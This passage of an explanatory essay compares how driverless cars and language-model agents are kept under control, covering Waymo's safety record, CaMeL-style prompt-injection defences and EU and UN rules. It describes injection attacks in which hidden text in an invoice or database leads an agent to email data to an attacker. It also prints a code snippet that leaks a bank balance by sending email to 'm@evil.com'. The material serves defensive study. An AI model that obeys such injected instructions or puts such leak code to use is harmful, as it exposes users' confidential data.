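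Raising B to allow for harder braking makes the rule safer but spreads traffic out. If the car ahead could stop instantly, the gap in the example would have to be 65.4 metres. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues want regulators to set these values. Regulators could then change a number and predict the effect, which they can't do with the trade-offs inside Tesla's network.

Like any check against a list of detected objects, the calculation fails if perception misses the car ahead. RSS has a separate rule for places with limited visibility, which matters for the pedestrian behind the van. That rule also depends on assumptions about how fast someone hidden there might step out.

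### Waymo's learned checker

Waymo calls the validation layer that separately checks its cars' trajectories "AI-based". It says the layer applies traffic laws and hard physical limits using techniques that include reinforcement learning, so the layer is not simply a list of provable rules.

Learning is useful in this layer because traffic rules have exceptions. Crossing a solid line is normally illegal, but it is the right thing to do when a police officer waves traffic around a crash. A checker with only fixed rules might block that manoeuvre, which is the brittleness that Wayve's Badrinarayanan complained about. But nobody can prove that a learned checker will reject every dangerous trajectory. Waymo has to estimate from tests how often the layer misses a dangerous trajectory and how often it stops a good one, and its published descriptions of the layer include neither figure.

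It is also unclear how independent the validation layer is. According to Waymo, the decoder that generates trajectories also produces signals for validating them. If the layer relies heavily on those signals, one mistake could both produce a bad trajectory and keep the layer from detecting it.

A checker for a car also needs a safe alternative when it rejects a plan. Braking is usually enough on a quiet street but can be dangerous on a fast road with a lorry close behind. Blocking an action is easier for an accounting agent, because a suspicious payment can usually wait until a person reviews it.

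### Instructions hidden in an invoice

Language-model agents are vulnerable to prompt injection, a threat with no close equivalent in driving. An attacker hides instructions in text that the agent reads as data, and the model follows them. An invoice might contain a line telling the agent to email the company's ledger to a stranger. Training can make models better at ignoring such lines, but an attacker can keep trying new wordings. Willison (2025) argues in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that a defence which catches 99% of attacks fails for this reason.

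Google DeepMind's CaMeL (2025) limits what instructions hidden in untrusted text can do, even when a model follows them. It builds on Willison's earlier proposal to use one model that has tools but never reads untrusted text and another that reads the text but has no tools. CaMeL adds ordinary code that runs the plan and enforces rules about data.

Suppose the user asks an agent to pay the latest invoice from a supplier called Acme. The planning model sees only that request and writes a short program, along these lines:

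```
invoice = get_latest_invoice("Acme")
details = reader("Find the account number and amount", invoice)
send_payment(to=details.account, amount=details.amount)
```

The second line sends the invoice to the reading model, which returns an account number and an amount. If the invoice also contains a request to email the ledger, nothing happens, because the program has no step that sends email.

An attacker could put a false account number in the invoice instead. The program would run as planned and pay the attacker. CaMeL therefore labels each value with its source, and the code that runs the program checks these labels against a policy. If an account number came from an invoice, the policy can allow payment only to approved accounts and refer any others to a person. Willison worries that people who receive too many of these requests will start approving everything.

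*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) states the general principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. According to the paper, general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees, and it recommends agents with deliberately limited abilities.

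### The price in completed tasks

CaMeL's planner must write its program before it sees any data, so it can't revise it after reading something unexpected. It must also know the format of every tool's output in advance. Strict policies block some legitimate actions as well as attacks.

Estimates of the share of tasks that agents complete under CaMeL vary widely. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives a figure of 67% on AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with planted attacks. In reruns reported in *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks (30%). The reruns used an adapted version of the software, which may partly explain the lower figure.

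Comparisons within one study are more informative. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with its policy checks on and off. Some attacks succeeded with the checks off and none with them on, but the checks roughly halved CaMeL's task success, to 37.5%.

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested the two-model design alone, with no policies about data. On multi-step professional tasks, it lowered success rates by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Better planners seem to lose less from having to plan without seeing the data.

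### What CaMeL guarantees

If the user's request is honest and the code works as intended, untrusted text cannot add a step to the plan, but it can still influence which of the planned steps the agent takes. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, apply the design to agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen. Their planner writes a program with branches for everything it expects to see. An attacker can make a page look like something else so that the agent takes the branch that leads to a malicious website. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) treats this as a separate security problem, because every action the agent takes was in the approved plan.

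Tallam and Miller point out other gaps in CaMeL. It treats the user's prompt as trusted, though an attacker may have persuaded the user to paste it in. An instruction hidden in a document could appear in the agent's summary, and a person might follow it. A program can also reveal a secret number without sending it, by contacting a website that many times.

Even the code that tracks data can have subtle faults. Garby and colleagues describe a leak that works roughly like this:

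```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL changes a variable's label only when it runs a line that sets the variable. If the balance is high, the fourth line doesn't set `rich`, so `rich` keeps its public label. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is above the threshold.

To rule out such leaks, Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language that labels every value, and proved its security properties in the proof checker Lean. The proofs cover the program that actually calls the model, and they allow an explicit override when the user wants the agent to act on an untrusted file. An agent written in this language completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL without its checks, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

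In both successful attacks, the user told the agent to read a file and make whatever payment it specified, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Labels can't distinguish the original file from the altered one, because the user asked the agent to follow the file's instructions. About two thirds of the task and attack combinations in the test were much easier to stop, because the attack needed a tool that a sensible plan for the task would never use.

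The proofs also show that if a plan contains no overrides, even a fully compromised planning model can do only what the policies allow. This gives strong control over a model whose reasoning nobody can read, but it depends on how good the policies are. A rule that permits payments to approved suppliers would let a bad planner pay one of them ten times too much, unless another rule limits the amount.

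### A message that becomes an instruction

Dividing an agent into modules can undo CaMeL's protection. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each with its own CaMeL defence. One queried a database of job applicants, one sent messages, and an orchestrator directed the other two. The user asked the system to send a summary of the applicants to a colleague, Julie. An attacker had hidden in the database an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

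The database agent and the orchestrator both handled the text as untrusted data, and their plans did not change. But the orchestrator put the summary inside its request to the messaging agent, which treated that request as the user's instruction. The messaging agent's planner read the hidden line, added an email step and sent the applicants' data to the attacker.

Peters-Gill and colleagues' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits every message between agents into an instruction that the receiving planner can read and a set of values that it can't. Code keeps anything that came from a tool out of the instruction. They tested it against 949 attacks for each model.

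| Model | Attacks that succeed with no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Every attack that got past the separate defences used this route between agents. On the professional tasks, multi-CaMeL lowered success by a further 3.2 points on average. It works because the developers defined what the interface may carry, so nobody has to read the messages as they pass. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without any defence, but Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that stronger attacks that adapt to the model have succeeded against every frontier model in large-scale tests.

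### How many miles are enough?

The other way to oversee an unreadable system is to let it act and count its failures. Kalra and Paddock, in *Driving to Safety*, a 2016 report from the research organisation RAND, calculated how much driving this takes. They started from the US rate of 1.09 deaths per 100 million miles. If a car causes deaths at a rate F per mile, the chance that it drives n miles without one is (1 − F)ⁿ. To be 95% confident that the car is no worse than the human rate, testers need enough miles that a car at that rate would get through them without a death only 5% of the time:

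n = ln(0.05) / ln(1 − 0.0000000109) ≈ 275 million miles.

A car as dangerous as the average human driver would have about three deaths over that distance on average, so having none is good evidence that the car is safer. One death in the test would raise the requirement to about 435 million miles. Estimating the car's death rate to within 20% would take about 8.8 billion miles. Kalra and Paddock concluded that companies could not prove their cars safe by test-driving them before release. The human rate has hardly changed since. The U.S. Department of Transportation's *Trump’s Transportation Department Announces Record-Low Traffic Deaths & Fatality Rates in 2025* (2026) puts it at 1.10 deaths per 100 million miles, which would require about 272 million miles without a death.

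### What Waymo's record supports

By the end of June 2026, Waymo's cars had driven 271.3 million miles with no human driver, almost exactly the distance in Kalra and Paddock's calculation. Waymo compares its cars' crashes with those of human drivers in the same areas, regardless of who was at fault.

| Crashes per million miles | Waymo | Human drivers | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Serious injury or death | 0.01 | 0.21 | −95% |
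| Any reported injury | 0.67 | 3.77 | −82% |
| Airbag deployed in any vehicle | 0.29 | 1.61 | −82% |

The top row corresponds to about three crashes, compared with about 58 that human drivers would have had. This is strong evidence that the cars cause or suffer far fewer serious crashes on the roads they use. It doesn't establish anything about deaths alone, because Waymo's figures combine deaths with serious injuries. The 275-million-mile calculation also works only if there are no deaths, and the national death rate includes motorways, which Waymo's human benchmarks leave out.

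Waymo produced the comparison itself, but anyone can check it, because it uses crash reports that companies must file with NHTSA and Waymo publishes the underlying data. Waymo raises the human injury figure by almost half to account for the estimated 32% of injury crashes that nobody reports to the police. This adjustment favors Waymo, but it is much too small to explain an 82% difference. The Insurance Institute for Highway Safety, an independent body funded by insurers, made its own estimate. Its *Waymo's driverless cars crash less often than people* counts 64 crashes serious enough to report to the police in about 50 million driverless miles.

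A good average can hide a specific fault. The same fleet kept passing stopped school buses in Austin, and these figures don't include violations that injure nobody. The record also covers many versions of the software. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues argue that changing a single line of planning code means restarting the count, because the change may have introduced a new kind of failure. That is too strict for most changes. An update that affects only parking, for example, leaves most of the earlier evidence intact. But Waymo retrains its models continually. If the fleet drove five million miles a week, one version would have to stay in use for 55 weeks to reach 275 million miles.

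Companies fill the gap with simulation, which has a similar difficulty. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues point out that a simulator can predict one version's crash rate accurately and still be wrong about the next. If the new version makes an odd movement that confuses human drivers, the simulator may miss the resulting crash because its model of human drivers doesn't include their reaction to that movement.

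Waymo uses a safety case, not the crash record, to decide in advance whether new software is ready. The miles driven afterward test whether the safety case was right, and people on the road bear the risk if it was wrong. The injury results have been very good.

### Counting failures in language-model agents

Nobody can draw up a table like Waymo's for language-model agents, because their work has no unit comparable to the mile. A thousand tasks could be spelling corrections or bank transfers, and the number of tokens an agent produces is a poor measure of how much harm it could have done. Human error rates for the same work are rarely available, and there is no general duty to report failures comparable to the one for driverless cars.

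Attackers also make past results less reliable because, unlike pedestrians near a self-driving car, they study the system to find where it will fail. When multi-CaMeL stopped all 949 attacks on a model, the 95% confidence interval for its failure rate ran from zero to 0.4%. That range applies only to attacks like those in the test, and an attacker can use a different kind.

For a narrow job, a company can create its own measure. If an agent reconciles ledger entries, the company can measure errors per entry by checking a random sample against its bookkeepers' work. By Kalra and Paddock's formula, about 30,000 checked entries without a mistake would support the claim that the error rate is below one in 10,000. The company would have to repeat much of this work when it changed the model, the instructions or the type of account. It would also need to count large errors separately, since one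 false payment of a million pounds matters more than a hundred punctuation errors.

### What regulators ask for

The main rules for these systems require human control and evidence of safety, and leave the internal design to the developer. The draft UN regulation on automated driving that a UN working party adopted in January 2026 requires manufacturers to present a safety case, have their safety management audited, pass tests, and monitor their cars in use. It does not require the planner to work from a readable list of objects, so an end-to-end network could qualify if the manufacturer's evidence were good enough.

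The EU's AI Act comes closer to requiring readable systems. Article 12 requires high-risk AI systems to record events automatically, so that people can identify risks and monitor how the system is working. Article 14 requires that the people in charge can understand the system's abilities and limits, interpret and override its output, and stop the system. A log of inputs, outputs and interventions could plausibly satisfy Article 12 without recording what passes between modules, although failures would then be harder to trace. Article 14 is about the system's output and a person's power to intervene. Neither article requires a safety case by that name.

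Most of these duties were originally due to apply from 2 August 2026. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed postponing them to December 2027 at the latest, and to August 2028 for AI built into regulated products. Neither article applies directly to self-driving cars, which the Act leaves mostly to the EU's vehicle-approval rules. They would usually not cover an agent that reconciles a company's accounts either, because ordinary bookkeeping is not on the list of high-risk uses, though they would cover an agent that scored people's creditworthiness. The company using the accounting agent would have to decide for itself what to log and which payments need a person's approval.
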